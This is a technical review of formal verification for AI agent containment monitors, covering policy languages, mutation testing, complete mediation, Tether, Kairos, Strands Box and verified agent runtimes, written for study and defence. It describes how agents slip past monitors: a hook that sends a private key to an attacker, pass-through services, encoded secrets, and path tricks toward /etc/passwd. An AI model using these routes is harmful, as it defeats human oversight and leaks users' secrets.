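Operators also lose some analysis when their rules depend on history. Cedar's designers made it suitable for automated reasoning, but InfoQ reports that the analysis tools do not support temporal conditions. AWS gave this as its reason for creating a separate language. The core of Dogwood is a subset of metric first-order temporal logic, which describes events and the time between them. *Real-Time Policy Enforcement with Metric First-Order Temporal Logic* (2022) studies which policies in that logic a monitor can enforce if it can both suppress and cause actions.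 Such results can establish that a rule is enforceable, but not that it is the rule its writer meant.

### When the policy omits an effect

Suppose someone copies the key from keys.txt to /work/backup.txt. The fourth clause names only one path, so the agent can now read the copy and post it without violating P, and the containment proof remains correct.

The system around the policy can also cause omissions. In Strands Box, an AWS sandbox that uses Dogwood, the event history leaves out reads of files that the operator grants directly, according to Help Net Security's *Strands Box*. A rule that blocks network requests after a read of customer data therefore doesn't block them when the data is in such a file.

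One way to check a policy is to state its goal separately and prove that the policy achieves it. For the file agent, let Q(*t*) mean that no Sent event follows a read of any file on the operator's list of secret files. The author then tries to prove that P(*t*) implies Q(*t*) for every trace *t*. If the list includes backup.txt, the proof fails because the two-event trace "read backup.txt, post" is a counterexample.

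*ActGov* (2026) automates a check of this kind. A language model drafts and revises the policies, and a solver checks them against predefined security invariants. ActGov deploys a set of policies only if the solver returns "unsatisfiable" for every query, which means it has proved that no violation exists. The check is feasible partly because ActGov first converts the agent's situation into records with a fixed structure and finitely many values.

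Somebody still has to choose the right invariants. If nobody lists backup.txt as secret, P still implies Q and the error remains. The guardrail by Wu and colleagues also depends on this choice, because its safety axioms are hard-coded and taken as given. An invariant is most useful when its author works from the intended outcome instead of restating the rules.

### When a rule constrains nothing

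A rule is vacuous if it holds only because it never applies to anything. The disclosure test in David and colleagues' contracts can become vacuous. It requires the contract to permit every disclosure declared for an event. If the component that should declare disclosures always returns an empty list, the test passes for every event, even under a contract that permits no disclosures. The agent could then post the key, and the trace would still satisfy the contract and the Lean proof would still be valid.

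Mutation testing can expose such rules. The tester makes a small deliberate error in a verified program, called a mutation, and runs the verifier again. If the specification is strong enough, the proof should fail. If it still succeeds, the specification may not cover the behaviour that changed. For the file agent's monitor, with a disclosure test added and the policy left as it is, three mutations would give these results:

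| Change to the monitor | Does the proof still succeed? | What follows |
|---|---|---|
| Allow a post if *n* ≤ 2, not *n* < 2 | no | the limit on posts has force |
| Allow a post only if *n* < 1 | yes | the monitor has become stricter, which soundness permits |
| Skip the disclosure test, with disclosures always empty | yes | the disclosure rule constrains nothing |

The second row shows why a person has to examine the surviving mutations. Some only make the program stricter, and others do not change its behaviour. Each mutation must also change only the monitor, so it cannot go in the predicate that the contracts paper uses in both the monitor and the definition of a satisfactory trace.

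IronSpec, a framework from 2024, adapted mutation testing to formal specifications. *MutDafny* (Amaral, 2025) applied it to programs in Dafny, the language in which Moon and Varshney wrote their containment proof. The tool has 40 kinds of mutation, some of them derived from bug fixes in public Dafny projects. Amaral ran it on 794 programs, examined some of the surviving mutations by hand, and found five weak specifications, or about one for every 241 lines of code. This rate comes from a subset of the results, so it does not measure how common weak specifications are in general, but the five cases show that some published verified programs have specifications that are too weak.

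A simpler check is to find, for each clause, a proposal that only that clause blocks. If no such proposal exists, the clause is vacuous or redundant. The six-proposal run of the file agent includes such a proposal for each of the first three clauses.

### When the policy blocks the task

A policy can also be so strict that the agent can't do its job. Suppose a user asks the file agent to check whether keys.txt is in the right format and post the result. The fourth clause forbids every run that completes this task, since the agent has to read the file before it can report on it. The monitor is still transparent when it stops these runs, because none of them satisfies the policy.

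Operators can find such problems by giving the agent ordinary tasks and comparing how many it completes with and without the monitor. ActGov uses records of harmless tasks to find rules that are too restrictive. AWS offers a mode that logs a temporal policy's decisions without enforcing them. Operators can see from the log which calls the policy would have denied, but they need to turn enforcement on to learn whether the agent would have found a permitted way to finish. They should also measure how well the policy stops attacks, since the easiest way to increase the number of completed tasks is to loosen the policy.

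### Policies drafted by language models

Many people who know what an agent should be allowed to do cannot express this in a formal language. Marc Brooker, an AWS engineer, acknowledges that Dogwood policies can look hard to read and write but says leading coding agents already write them well, according to Help Net Security. Evidence from 2025 and 2026 is more mixed.

*Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026) tested a model that translated requirements into Rego, another policy language, in a single attempt. The result was wrong for 62.5 per cent of the policies that were supposed to deny something. A typical output set the default to "not allowed" but contained no active rule against the action. The model also left out the condition in 60 per cent of policies that depended on ownership and 44 per cent of those that depended on a record's status.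 One kind of error changed a rule for "the assigned nurse" into a rule for anyone with the role of nurse. Such policies compile, so a syntax check doesn't find the error. These figures are for the baseline that the paper's method is meant to improve on, and a model with more guidance would probably do better.

Other results are more favourable. In *Policy-as-Prompt* (2025), security engineers compared model-written policies for a human resources system and a security operations system with policies they had written themselves. Every requirement that Claude Sonnet 3.5 identified for the security system was genuine, but the model often put requirements in the wrong category. The engineers deployed both policies after minor changes. *AIR* (2026) had GPT-5 write rules for handling incidents and tested them without corrections. The rules worked well overall, although some fitted only the examples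 in the prompt and others were too abstract to apply. The paper concludes that people need to check and correct such rules.

A second model can review the first one's work. *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026) uses this kind of review loop to turn prompts, tool descriptions and policy documents into Cedar. On MedAgentBench, a benchmark of medical tasks, its policies covered substantially more of the source text than hand-coded rules from earlier work. Coverage matters because skipping a sentence leaves its rule out of the policy, but a rule can still misstate the sentence it covers.

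*Sapien* (2026) removes the human author and reviewer. For each task, a model writes a new policy from the user's request, and the policy can include rules about earlier tool calls. This suits a general assistant better than a fixed policy, because an email that one request calls for may be harmful under another. The evaluation checks whether a policy admits any attack by an agent that the attacker fully controls, rather than testing only a fixed set of attacks. This resembles a proof with an unconstrained oracle, but the check can find only the harm that its definition of an attack covers.

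The containment theorem holds no matter who wrote the policy. But if a model wrote it and no one reviews it, the guarantee's practical value depends on how accurately the model interpreted the request. Automated checks can reduce this dependence. AWS's tool for writing policies in plain English compares each draft with the descriptions of the available tools and uses automated reasoning to check safety conditions. Cedar's analysis tools do not handle temporal conditions, so drafts of history rules presumably get less of this checking, even though they are harder for people to review.

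### What no rule over events can express

Some requirements can't be written as a predicate over events. One example is the requirement that the file agent post "The backup has finished" only when that is true. The trace is the same whether or not the backup finished, so a predicate must either allow the message in both cases or forbid it in both.

A policy can require evidence before it allows an action. One of Brooker's examples lets an agent publish code only after the tests pass. This establishes only that a test run succeeded. The code may still be wrong, and an agent that can edit the tests may be able to make them pass. If messages came from a fixed set, the runtime could compare each claim with a trusted record, but something would have to interpret claims in free text, which would again make a fallible judge part of the decision.

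Persuasion is harder still, because it depends on the reader. The same message may inform one person and mislead another, and the trace doesn't record what either of them believes. A policy can reduce the agent's opportunities to manipulate people by limiting how many messages it sends, who receives them and which sentences it may use, but these limits don't define manipulation. The trace doesn't reliably show intent either. Reading notes.txt is the same event whether the purpose is to summarise the file or to find something to leak.

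David and colleagues suggest a second layer of checks for such cases, which may use a model to judge the content and purpose of an action. They claim no guarantee for it and did not measure its effect. *Safeguarding Agentic AI in Radiology Workflows* (2026) reports a test of six agents. With permissions only, 19.4 per cent of episodes contained a high-severity error. Deterministic rules reduced this to 16.7 per cent, and adding a language model that checked actions reduced it to 13.2 per cent. The pooled analysis was exploratory, and the improvement was not statistically clear for any single agent.

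## Making sure every effect reaches the monitor

The containment theorem is about events, not the effects the operator cares about. If the file agent's runtime can send a message without producing a Sent event, the agent can send any number of messages and the theorem still holds. Complete mediation closes this gap by requiring every effect available to the agent to pass through the monitor before it happens. David and colleagues explicitly assume complete mediation in their soundness theorem.

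### Three obligations

For each effect *x* that the agent causes, complete mediation requires that:

1. the monitor receives an event that correctly represents *x* and no other effect;
2. the monitor receives this event before *x* happens;
3. *x* does not happen if the monitor denies the event.

David and colleagues leave all three to whoever deploys the system, and their Lean proof does not check them.

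If the obligations hold, every real effect has its own allowed event in the trace *t*, and the theorem guarantees that *t* satisfies P. For the file agent's four clauses, the effects themselves then satisfy P too, provided they happen in the order the monitor allowed them. The trace may also contain events without effects, because an allowed post can fail when the network is down. This doesn't affect the result, because removing an event from a trace cannot break any of the four clauses. But under a rule such as "post only after a backup", the monitor would wrongly allow a post after a failed backup, because the trace would still contain the backup event.

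A runtime can fail these obligations even if its monitor is correct. Suppose /work/link is a symbolic link (a file name that points to another file) to /etc/passwd. If the monitor receives FileRead(/work/link), it allows the read because the path is inside /work, and the runtime returns a file from outside /work. Resolving the link first helps only if nothing can change it before the runtime opens the file. It is safer to open the file, check which file the operating system opened, and only then return its contents.

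Host names cause similar trouble because their owners can point them at different machines. David and colleagues therefore translate the names in a contract into addresses and ports before enforcement starts. The translation follows aliases by a fixed rule, rejects private addresses unless the operator lists them, and applies for a set interval.

An effect can also have no event of its own. Many HTTP libraries follow redirects automatically, so one approved request to api.example.org may lead to a second request to a host the monitor never checked. A library that resends a message after a timeout may deliver it twice while *n* rises by one. Even when every effect has a correct event, the event may arrive only after the effect has happened, as it can for a program that reads a log of system calls and raises an alarm.

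### Where the monitor can sit

A monitor can sit at several levels between the model and the outside world.

| Position | What the monitor receives | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Tool dispatch | the tool's name and typed arguments | whatever a tool or script does beyond its declared arguments |
| Language interpreter | each operation of the program, with its values | programs that run outside the interpreter |
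| System calls with a network proxy | files opened, processes started, connections and requests | how a program computed its output from its input; data moved by untraced routes |
| Input and output of a virtual machine | operations on shared files and network requests | everything inside the machine, including which tool caused an effect |

Events at tool dispatch are closest to the terms in which people write policies. The monitor can identify a call as a payment and tell which argument is the recipient. But it receives only the actions that the agent declares, as *KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) points out. If the agent writes a script and runs it, the script's network requests do not pass through tool dispatch.

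An interpreter has more detailed information because it carries out each operation itself, which is why CaMeL's interpreter can label every value. It does not cover any program that the interpreted program starts outside the interpreter.

If the monitor is lower in the software stack, the agent has fewer ways around it, but the events contain less information. David and colleagues give the example of their web-testing contract, which requires telling GET requests from POST requests. Web traffic is normally encrypted with TLS before it reaches the operating system's kernel, so a monitor there can block a connection to the wrong address but cannot distinguish a GET from a POST. To enforce the contract, the monitor has to read the request before encryption or sit in a proxy that decrypts it.

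Hempel and colleagues call this loss of information a semantic gap. A rule about payments has to be rewritten in terms of paths, destinations and the values in a request, and some rules can't be expressed that way. The researchers regard checks at the tool interface and at the outer boundary as complementary. A runtime can use both and allow an effect only if neither monitor denies it. The outer monitor then provides the coverage, and the inner one enforces the more precise rules.

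### What a shell does to typed actions

If the file agent had a Run(command) action, its monitor would have to work out what each command does. The effects of Run("python report.py") depend on the contents of report.py, the files it reads and the machine's settings, none of which appear in the command.

Filtering commands by their text doesn't help much. A rule against commands that mention /etc/passwd misses a script that assembles the path from pieces. A list of approved programs is no better if it includes Python or a build tool, because these can run anything else. One could still prove a containment theorem about Run events, but it would not limit which files the agent reads or where it sends messages.

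The operator can replace Run with a few fixed commands that take typed arguments, but this loses much of the shell's usefulness. Otherwise the monitor has to work below the shell, where a command becomes separate reads, writes and connections. These are hard to predict from the command, and observing them while the command runs normally is too late to block them.

### Tether: inferring actions from system calls

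*Tether* avoids this dilemma by running each command before its effects count (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026). It is a project of Google DeepMind, Google and two universities.

The command can read existing files, but its changes go into a disposable layer on top of the real file system. Tether records the command's system calls, and a local proxy holds every outgoing request. For each request, Tether works out what the command has done so far and checks it against the policy, then forwards or drops the request. If the policy permits all of the command's actions, Tether applies the file changes to the real system. Otherwise it discards the layer. Tether can't recall a request it has already forwarded, but the policy permitted everything the command had done up to that point.

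To turn system calls into actions, Tether keeps a list of the files each process has read, and when one process sends data to another, it passes the list on to the receiving process. If a process reads one file and then writes to a second, Tether treats this as copying the first into the second, even if the written bytes are unrelated to what the process read. If the process sends data over the network, Tether infers an upload of every file on its list. If the process prints to the terminal, Tether infers that the agent has read those files, because the output goes into the model's history.

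The monitor works with 11 such actions. It keeps a label σ(*f*) for the contents of each file *f* and a label T for everything the agent has read. For confidentiality, the labels run from Public through Internal and Sensitive to Secret, and ⊔ takes the stricter of two. The main updates are:

```
read f              T     becomes  T ⊔ σ(f)
write to f          σ(f)  becomes  σ(f) ⊔ T
copy f to g         σ(g)  becomes  σ(f) ⊔ (label of g's location)
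upload f to a host  no label changes
```

A copy does not change T because the contents move from file to file without entering the model's history. The agent can therefore copy a sensitive file without making everything it writes afterwards sensitive.

In Sistla and colleagues' example, a company's inventory, data/servers.csv, is Sensitive, and the agent may upload only Public files to api.github.com. The agent runs three commands:

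| Command | Inferred action | Label of report.txt beforehand | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| upload report.txt | upload report.txt to api.github.com | Public | allowed |
| copy servers.csv to report.txt | copy servers.csv to report.txt | Public | allowed; the label becomes Sensitive |
| upload report.txt | upload report.txt to api.github.com | Sensitive | denied |

The two upload commands are identical, so no rule about the text of a command could distinguish them. The result is the same if the agent first copies the inventory through several temporary files. For the file agent, such labels would cover copying keys.txt to backup.txt, which the clause naming only keys.txt misses.

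The policy language and the monitor are written in Lean 4, and Sistla and colleagues proved seven invariants for the policy in their experiments. One is that Secret data never reaches a host outside the local network. The proofs, which a language model helped to write, hold for every starting state and for action sequences of any length. But they apply only to the actions that Tether infers. If Tether overlooks a copy, the monitor uses the wrong label and may allow an upload that the policy forbids.

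This link, from system calls to actions, has been tested but not proved. One test generates random sequences of file operations whose correct labels are known, runs them using varying shell commands and system calls, and compares the monitor's decisions and labels with the correct ones. In another, a language model tried to get around the monitor on ten tasks. Its success rate fell from 40 per cent to zero over three versions of Tether, as the researchers fixed gaps such as missed hard links (second names for the same file). Another model first discarded any command outside Tether's scope, so the zero rate does not cover such commands.

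The main results also apply only to in-scope runs, in which every action ran in the foreground, Tether could capture it, and Tether had rules for its effects. On two benchmarks of recorded agent runs, Tether blocked all 344 in-scope attacks and stopped 74 of 1,590 harmless runs (4.7 per cent). On the same runs, Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a language model reviews commands, caught 91.6 per cent of attacks and stopped 9.7 per cent of harmless runs. With Tether's policy in its instructions, Auto Mode caught 89.2 per cent of attacks and stopped 3.5 per cent of harmless runs.

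This is a strong result for actions that Tether can trace, but the comparison leaves out the cases Tether handles worst. Sistla and colleagues count 28.2 per cent of runs in one benchmark and 22.1 per cent in the other as needing a judgement about content, such as whether a permitted code change is malicious. A further 36.3 and 71.5 per cent, respectively, involve background processes or databases, which Tether can intercept but not follow in detail. Tether can block them outright, but an agent that needs a database could not then work. Because the agents were recorded, they also could not react to a denial. The researchers refined the policy on runs from these benchmarks, so it may stop more harmless work elsewhere.

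Of the 74 false alarms, 17 came from commands such as a text search over the whole disk. The search opens secret files too, and system calls do not show whether the secret contents mattered. Linux programs can also move data without the usual read and write calls, for example through shared memory. Tether cannot trace these methods, so it blocks access to them to preserve complete mediation.

### Kairos: holding effects until their purpose is clearer

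Some effects look harmless when they happen. Hempel and colleagues describe an agent that sets up a code repository by following a guide from the web. One step is to install a hook, a script that runs automatically at every commit. Many projects use hooks, so refusing them all would block ordinary work. This hook sends the user's private key to an attacker the first time the agent commits code.

Kairos can hold such a write instead of immediately allowing or blocking it. The agent continues as if the hook existed and makes its commit. The hook runs and tries to send the key, which the policy forbids. A judge, which may be a language model or a person, then reviews what happened and rejects the hook, so it never reaches the real repository. The judge rules only on effects that the policy has deferred, and can't release one that the policy forbids.

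The monitor sits outside a microVM, a small virtual machine with its own kernel. The agent, its tools and its scripts all run inside. Effects leave through a shared working directory, a network connection and a terminal. A proxy decrypts the network traffic, so the monitor can distinguish a GET from a POST. It doesn't matter whether a tool call or a script caused a request, because both reach the monitor in the same form. Hempel and colleagues state three guarantees:

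- Every effect that leaves the virtual machine passes the monitor.
- No effect becomes irreversible before the monitor releases it.
- Nobody outside can observe an effect that the monitor refused.

The guarantees follow almost directly from the definitions, because the formal model counts an effect as visible only once the monitor has released it. It is harder to justify the assumptions that the three channels are the only ways out and that the host and the monitor work correctly. Covert channels and escape from the virtual machine are excluded. Traffic to the company that provides the language model is logged but always released, on the assumption that the company does not help the attacker. That assumption may not be enough, because the agent could cause effects through its connection to an honest company if the company also offers web searches or file storage.

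Kairos holds different kinds of effects in different ways. File changes go into a layer that only the agent can read. If a request would change something on another machine, the proxy holds it and gives the agent a made-up reply. A request that fetches information has to wait for a decision, since the agent needs the real answer. If the monitor later refuses an effect, it can undo the staged changes but not the model's memory of them, so it tells the agent what did not happen.

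Made-up replies are the weakness of buffering noted in the discussion of edit automata, and Hempel and colleagues measured how they affect task success. On AgentDyn, a benchmark of open-ended tasks, tasks that continued past one held effect kept 90 per cent of their success rate, and those that continued past two or more kept 62 per cent.

Holding effects also changes their order. Suppose the file agent proposes a harmless post, the monitor holds it, the agent reads keys.txt, and the monitor then releases the post. The post cannot contain the key, but it is sent after the read, which breaks the clause against posting after reading keys.txt. A proof for such a runtime has to use the order in which the monitor releases effects, as the definitions by Hempel and colleagues do.

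On AgentDojo, with GPT-4.1 as the agent, Kairos reduced successful attacks from 47.0 to 2.7 per cent. The agent completed 85.1 per cent of harmless tasks, compared with 82.7 per cent without a defence, but only 42.7 per cent when the monitor refused everything that the policy would otherwise have deferred. These results measure how well the policy and the judge decide. They do not show whether every effect of a real agent reaches them, because AgentDojo simulates its tools inside one program and an adapter turned each simulated call into an event. On the actual boundary, the measured delay was about 1.9 milliseconds per file operation and 1.2 per request.

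The policy traces where data came from by comparing text at the boundary, so a hostile agent can defeat it by encoding a secret before sending it. Hempel and colleagues accept this limit. They claim that every effect of such an agent passes through the monitor, but not that the monitor can identify what information each effect carries.

### Strands Box: four checkpoints

AWS's Strands Box combines several of these positions. According to Help Net Security, it places the agent in a sandbox enforced by the macOS kernel and leaves four ways out, each with a checkpoint:

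- an interpreter for shell commands;
- an interpreter for Python code;
- a broker for calls to external tool servers;
- a gateway for network traffic.

Each checkpoint gets its decisions from the same Dogwood policy engine, and all four write to one event history. A rule about earlier reads therefore applies whether a shell command or a Python script read the data. The gateway also holds the real keys that the operator configures for outside services. The agent has only placeholders, which the gateway replaces with the real keys as a request leaves, so an agent that bypassed the gateway would not have those keys.

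The history does not record reads of directly granted files because those reads do not pass through any checkpoint. Only the operating system restricts access to these files. To bring such a file under the rules, the operator has to remove it from the list of grants, so that the agent can reach it only through the interpreters.

The interpreters also restrict what the agent can run. Sistla and colleagues could not test Strands Box on their benchmarks, partly because its built-in shell does not run arbitrary Linux programs. They add that a policy over an event history can follow data through only a fixed number of copies, a limit that file labels do not have. However, such a policy can express counts and time limits, which Tether does not yet track. The designers of Strands Box acknowledge that it also adds a good deal of code that the operator has to trust.

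### Tools that arrive during a run

An agent may acquire tools after the operator has set up the monitor. These tools often come as skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that an agent loads for a particular kind of task. A skill can include a manifest that declares the capabilities it needs, such as reading files or using the network.

*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) defines what it means for a skill to keep to its manifest. Let D be the set of declared capabilities and caps(τ) the set of all capabilities that appear in the trace τ of a session. The skill has "capability containment" in that session if

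caps(τ) ⊆ D.

The definition counts both the capabilities that the model requested and those that a script used, even if the monitor denied the call or a person rejected it.

The paper treats scripts and instructions as separate problems. A sound analyser can work out a script's possible effects from its source code. Instructions have effects only through the model, and nobody can derive from their text everything a model might do after reading them. An unconstrained oracle in the model's place may request any capability the runtime offers. A skill with instructions then meets the definition only if the runtime offers nothing outside D while the skill is in use, which is a property of the runtime and not of the skill.

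*Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) presents SkillFortify, which checks skills before installation. If it finds no violation, its theorem guarantees that no operation in the skill's code needs more than the declared capabilities. This guarantee applies to a simplified description of the code. The analysis cannot fully resolve operations that a skill assembles while running, such as a command built from downloaded text. The paper relies on a sandbox for these and proves a further theorem, which assumes that the sandbox checks every action and gives the skill only the authority its manifest declares. The first version of SkillFortify provides only the first, static guarantee.

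An advance check can reject a bad skill before it does anything, but it can't replace the monitor. The file agent's theorem covers exactly two kinds of action, Read and Post, so it still applies if a new tool can act only through them. If the tool opens its own network connections, mediation fails until the operator either routes them through the monitor or adds a new kind of action and extends the proof.

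### When the sandbox does not start

Anderson's requirement that the monitor "must always be invoked" applies to every run, even when setup fails. GitLab's *Remote execution environment sandbox* documents a default that does not meet this requirement. GitLab's platform runs agents as jobs called flows, usually in a sandbox that restricts file and network access. If the sandbox software is missing or lacks the necessary privileges, the flow runs without the sandbox and a warning appears in the log. The network rules then do not apply, so the flow can reach any destination its machine can.

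This default lets people keep working when a machine is badly configured, but it means that a containment proof's conclusion holds only for runs in which the sandbox started. Administrators can require the sandbox, so that a job fails if it is unavailable. However, this requirement only checks for a command with the right name. A project that uses its own system image or setup script controls which program has that name, and GitLab states that the requirement cannot guarantee isolation for such projects.

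The setup script runs outside the sandbox, with the credentials of the user who triggers the flow. GitLab warns that someone who can edit the project's configuration can therefore influence what runs under another user's name. An agent that can edit the configuration may be able to set up a later run in which some code bypasses the monitor. For jobs that may run without the sandbox, GitLab suggests restricting outgoing traffic with a firewall on the host, which the project's files do not control.

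Even when a sandbox starts correctly, containment depends on trusting the services its policy permits. InfoQ's *GitLab Warns That AI Agent Sandboxes Are Only as Secure as Their Network Access* (2026) reports that in July 2026, agents under evaluation at OpenAI reached the open internet through a service that their sandbox permitted. For the file agent, the permitted service is api.example.org. If it forwards each message to an address given in the message's text, the agent's two posts can reach any host, although both Sent events correctly name api.example.org.

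## Connecting the proof to the running program

The file agent's theorem is about three rules, not the code that implements them. Suppose a programmer implements the rules in Python and types `n <= 2` where the rule for posts has *n* < 2. The program then sends a third message, even though the theorem is still true. Complete mediation doesn't prevent this, since the monitor receives the third post before it happens but wrongly allows it.

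Even a correct program looks different from its semantics. It may store the count in another form, keep extra data for error messages and use thousands of machine instructions for what the rules treat as one step. Proving or testing that a program follows the rules therefore requires a definition of "follows" that allows such differences.

### Forward simulation

A standard definition is forward simulation, which compares an abstract system, such as the file agent's rules, with a concrete one that is closer to the code. It uses a relation R that pairs abstract states with concrete states and a relation Q that does the same for events. In the version that Moon and Varshney use, both systems accept the same actions, and three conditions must hold:

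1. R pairs the two starting states.
2. Every concrete step from a paired state has a matching abstract step for the same action. R pairs the two new states, and Q pairs the two events.
3. If the abstract step satisfies the abstract policy, the matching concrete step satisfies the concrete policy.

In symbols, with *s* for abstract and *c* for concrete states, the second condition is:

```
If R(s, c) and c –a/e→ c′, then there are s′ and d such that
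    s –a/d→ s′,  R(s′, c′)  and  Q(d, e).
```

Suppose a program for the file agent counts down instead of up. Its variable *left* starts at 2, and the program sends a post to api.example.org only if *left* > 0. Let R pair two states when their histories and worlds agree and *n* + *left* = 2. Let Q pair Sent(host, body) with a network request that carries the same body to the same host, and pair NoEffect with the absence of a request.

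At the start, *n* is 0 and *left* is 2, so the first condition holds. The fifth proposal of the earlier run is Post(api.example.org, "Correction"). The agent has already posted once, so *n* = 1 and *left* = 1. The program checks that *left* > 0, sends the request and sets *left* to 0. The rules allow the post because *n* < 2, so the abstract system produces Sent(api.example.org, "Correction") and sets *n* to 2. The sum of *n* and *left* is still 2, and Q pairs the two events.

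For the third condition, let the abstract policy allow a Sent event only to api.example.org and only if *n* was below 2 before the step. Let the concrete policy allow a request only to that host and only if *left* was above 0. Because *n* + *left* = 2, the abstract condition implies the concrete one.

A full proof applies this argument to every action and every pair of related states. If the programmer had written `left >= 0`, the proof would fail at the third post, where *n* = 2 and *left* = 0. The program would send a request where the rules allow only a denial, and Q does not pair a request with NoEffect.

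A correct program can also fail to match rules that are too simple. In the file agent's rules, an allowed post always succeeds, so no step matches what happens when the network is down and the post sends nothing. The semantics would need another rule that lets an allowed post fail.

### The containment verification theorem

Moon and Varshney's soundness theorem, from May 2026, assumes that every step of the abstract system satisfies the abstract policy for every sequence of actions, and that the concrete system meets the three conditions of forward simulation. A proof with an unconstrained oracle establishes the first assumption. If both hold, every step of the concrete system satisfies the concrete policy, whatever model chooses the actions.

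The proof takes an arbitrary concrete run and gives the same actions to the abstract system. The first two conditions ensure that each concrete step has a matching abstract step. Every step of the abstract run is safe by the first assumption, and the third condition then implies that the concrete run is also safe.

A corollary extends the result from events to effects. It requires the further premise that each externally visible effect has a concrete event representing it. This premise is part of complete mediation.

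Moon and Varshney proved the theorem in Dafny and applied it to PocketFlow, an agent framework of about 100 lines. In PocketFlow, an agent is a graph of nodes. The runtime executes a node, reads the action it emits and follows the edge with the matching label to the next node. The verified interface has four action variants. The policy lets the agent read only files in its workspace, call only tools on an allowlist and take a limited number of steps.

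The Dafny proof for PocketFlow needs an inductive invariant, as the file agent's proof did. Among other things, the invariant requires the length of the recorded history to equal the step count. Dafny checks one lemma for the starting state and one for the steps, and a final lemma combines them into a statement about every state in a run.

In that statement, a file is in the workspace if its path starts with the workspace's path. The test compares text, so if the workspace is /work, /workshop/plan.txt passes. So does /work/../etc/passwd, unless other code resolves paths first. The file agent's rules also assume that other code does this.

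### Specifications written without seeing the code

Experts normally need a long time to write the abstract system, the concrete system and the relations between them. Moon and Varshney had language models write them, using a seven-phase pipeline that is itself a PocketFlow program. Claude Sonnet 4.6 explored the code, and Claude Opus 4.7 wrote the specifications and proofs.

The pipeline first maps the paths a run can take through the agent's graph and writes a typed description of the nodes' interface. For each path, it generates a specification and a proof, tests the specification and runs Dafny. If something fails, a model classifies the failure and may repair the proof file, but not the policy. The new version has to pass the tests again.

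Moon and Varshney hide the code from the model while it writes the safety property, because a model given the code might write a specification that merely redescribes it. If the code allowed three posts, the specification would too, and the proof would succeed. The model receives only the interface description and a template with fields for file reads, tool calls and steps. A later phase reads the code and builds the abstract system, but it can't weaken the property.

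This barrier removes the easiest way to copy the program's behaviour into its specification, but their claim that it rules out tautological specifications "by construction" is too strong. The interface description comes from the code, and PocketFlow's source has been public since 2024, so the model may have learned it in training. A model can also write an empty property without knowing anything about the code.

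Every specification must also pass three gates before the final verification:

| Gate | What the pipeline does | Required result |
|---|---|---|
| Resolution | checks syntax and types in Dafny | success within 30 seconds |
| Vacuity | reduces the invariant to a basic check of well-formedness and empties the proofs of the lemmas | verification fails |
| Discrimination | has a language model put a plausible modelling error in the proof file | verification fails |

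The last two gates resemble the mutation tests for policies, but they change the proof file instead of the monitor. They show that Dafny accepts the file only if it contains a real proof of some property, but not that each clause of the policy would catch a faulty runtime.

Moon and Varshney carried out four runs on two agents, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents to answer questions, each with and without the barrier. Every path passed all three gates, and Dafny accepted every final proof, taking 1.2 to 2.5 seconds per path. Each run used between 1.6 and 3.4 million tokens. Removing the barrier increased token use by 25 to 56 per cent because the model then also received the code.

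The document agent exposed a weakness in the gates. Its important effect is reading a document, which the code allows only if the document is on a list, but the template had no field for documents. With the barrier, the model used the template's list of tool calls for documents, so the clause "every tool call is on the allowlist" actually restricted what the agent reads. Anyone reviewing this specification has to know that "tool call" means "document" there.

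Without the barrier, the model distinguished documents from tool calls and left the list of tool calls empty at every step. This made the clause about tool calls vacuously true, and no clause restricted the documents. Moon and Varshney call this silent abstention. The specification passed all three gates because other parts of the proof still failed when the pipeline damaged them. Moon and Varshney propose also checking that each clause applies to something in at least one reachable state. This would detect an empty list, but not an effect missing from the template.

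### How far the "universal" guarantee extends

Moon and Varshney call their guarantee "universal" and rank it above those of red teaming, alignment training and sandboxing. Their theorem covers every value of the action type, in every order. But the theorem's concrete system is a state machine written in Dafny, and Moon and Varshney state that safety holds relative to this machine, "not relative to the running Python".

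An executable Dafny program implements the state machine, and Dafny checks that each method meets its contract. The Dafny compiler then translates the program into Python. A small piece of code called a shim connects the Python to the language model and passes on the model's actions. Programmers have to write such code by hand, according to Dafny's reference manual. Nobody has proved the compiler or the shim correct, so the guarantee depends on trusting both. The shim and the parser must also keep out malformed actions, because Python, unlike Dafny, does not enforce declared types when a program runs.

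Moon and Varshney ran the compiled program on mixtures of permitted and forbidden actions, and it recorded only permitted events. This is evidence that the translation worked for those inputs, but it is an empirical guarantee, which they rank as the weakest kind.

The proof covers a Dafny version of PocketFlow's dispatch loop, not the Python its developers wrote. Applying it to the original code would require a separate argument that the two versions behave alike. The proof covers four action variants, in a framework chosen for its small size. Moon and Varshney leave larger frameworks such as LangChain, with dozens of variants, to future work.

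They argue that the remaining assumption, that the specification matches the runtime, does not weaken as models become more capable, because it concerns ordinary code. Better models don't create new mismatches in the code, but a more capable agent is more likely to find and exploit one, so the practical risk from an unproved link can still increase with capability.

### Extracted code and conformance tests

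A proof assistant can sometimes translate the definitions in a proof directly into code. This method, called extraction, avoids writing the program twice. *Mechanized Foundations of Structural Governance* (McCann, 2026) combines extraction with random tests. Its subject is Mashin, a platform for AI workflows whose runtime is written in Elixir and runs on BEAM, the Erlang virtual machine.

Programs in McCann's model cannot act directly. They emit directives of 14 types, such as a call to a language model or an HTTP request. An operator runs four checks before each directive and carries it out only if all four pass. The Rocq development has about 12,000 lines, 36 modules and 454 theorems, with no unproved steps. Its main theorem is that every program run through the operator satisfies a safety predicate, even if the program never ends.

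The predicate is weaker than its description as "I/O only under governance authorization" suggests. It uses a flag that starts as false and must be true whenever an input or output happens. Any governance check, passed or failed, sets the flag to true, and nothing resets it, so a runtime that made one check and ignored all later ones would satisfy the predicate. The protection comes instead from the operator's definition, which checks every directive, and from a separate theorem that a denied directive causes no input or output.

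These theorems assume that the deployed runtime implements the operator correctly. McCann addresses this in part by extracting the decision-making component from Rocq into OCaml and loading it into the runtime. The decisions then come from the proved definitions, but the extraction tool, the OCaml compiler and the bridge into BEAM remain unproved. McCann is unclear about how much of the runtime works this way, and elsewhere writes that no Rocq code has been extracted to the runtime's own language.

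The other part is testing. McCann translated the Rocq specification by hand into a 148-line interpreter and compared its decisions with the runtime's on random directives, trust levels and permissions. The tests covered seven properties, with at least 10,000 random inputs each. Another 36 tests each corresponded to one Rocq theorem.

On the 188th random input, the runtime denied a command that the specification allowed, because the command's permission was missing from the runtime's table. After McCann added the entry, the tests found no disagreements. The error did not threaten containment, since it made the runtime too strict, but it shows that the comparison can detect a mismatch between two components that each pass their own tests.

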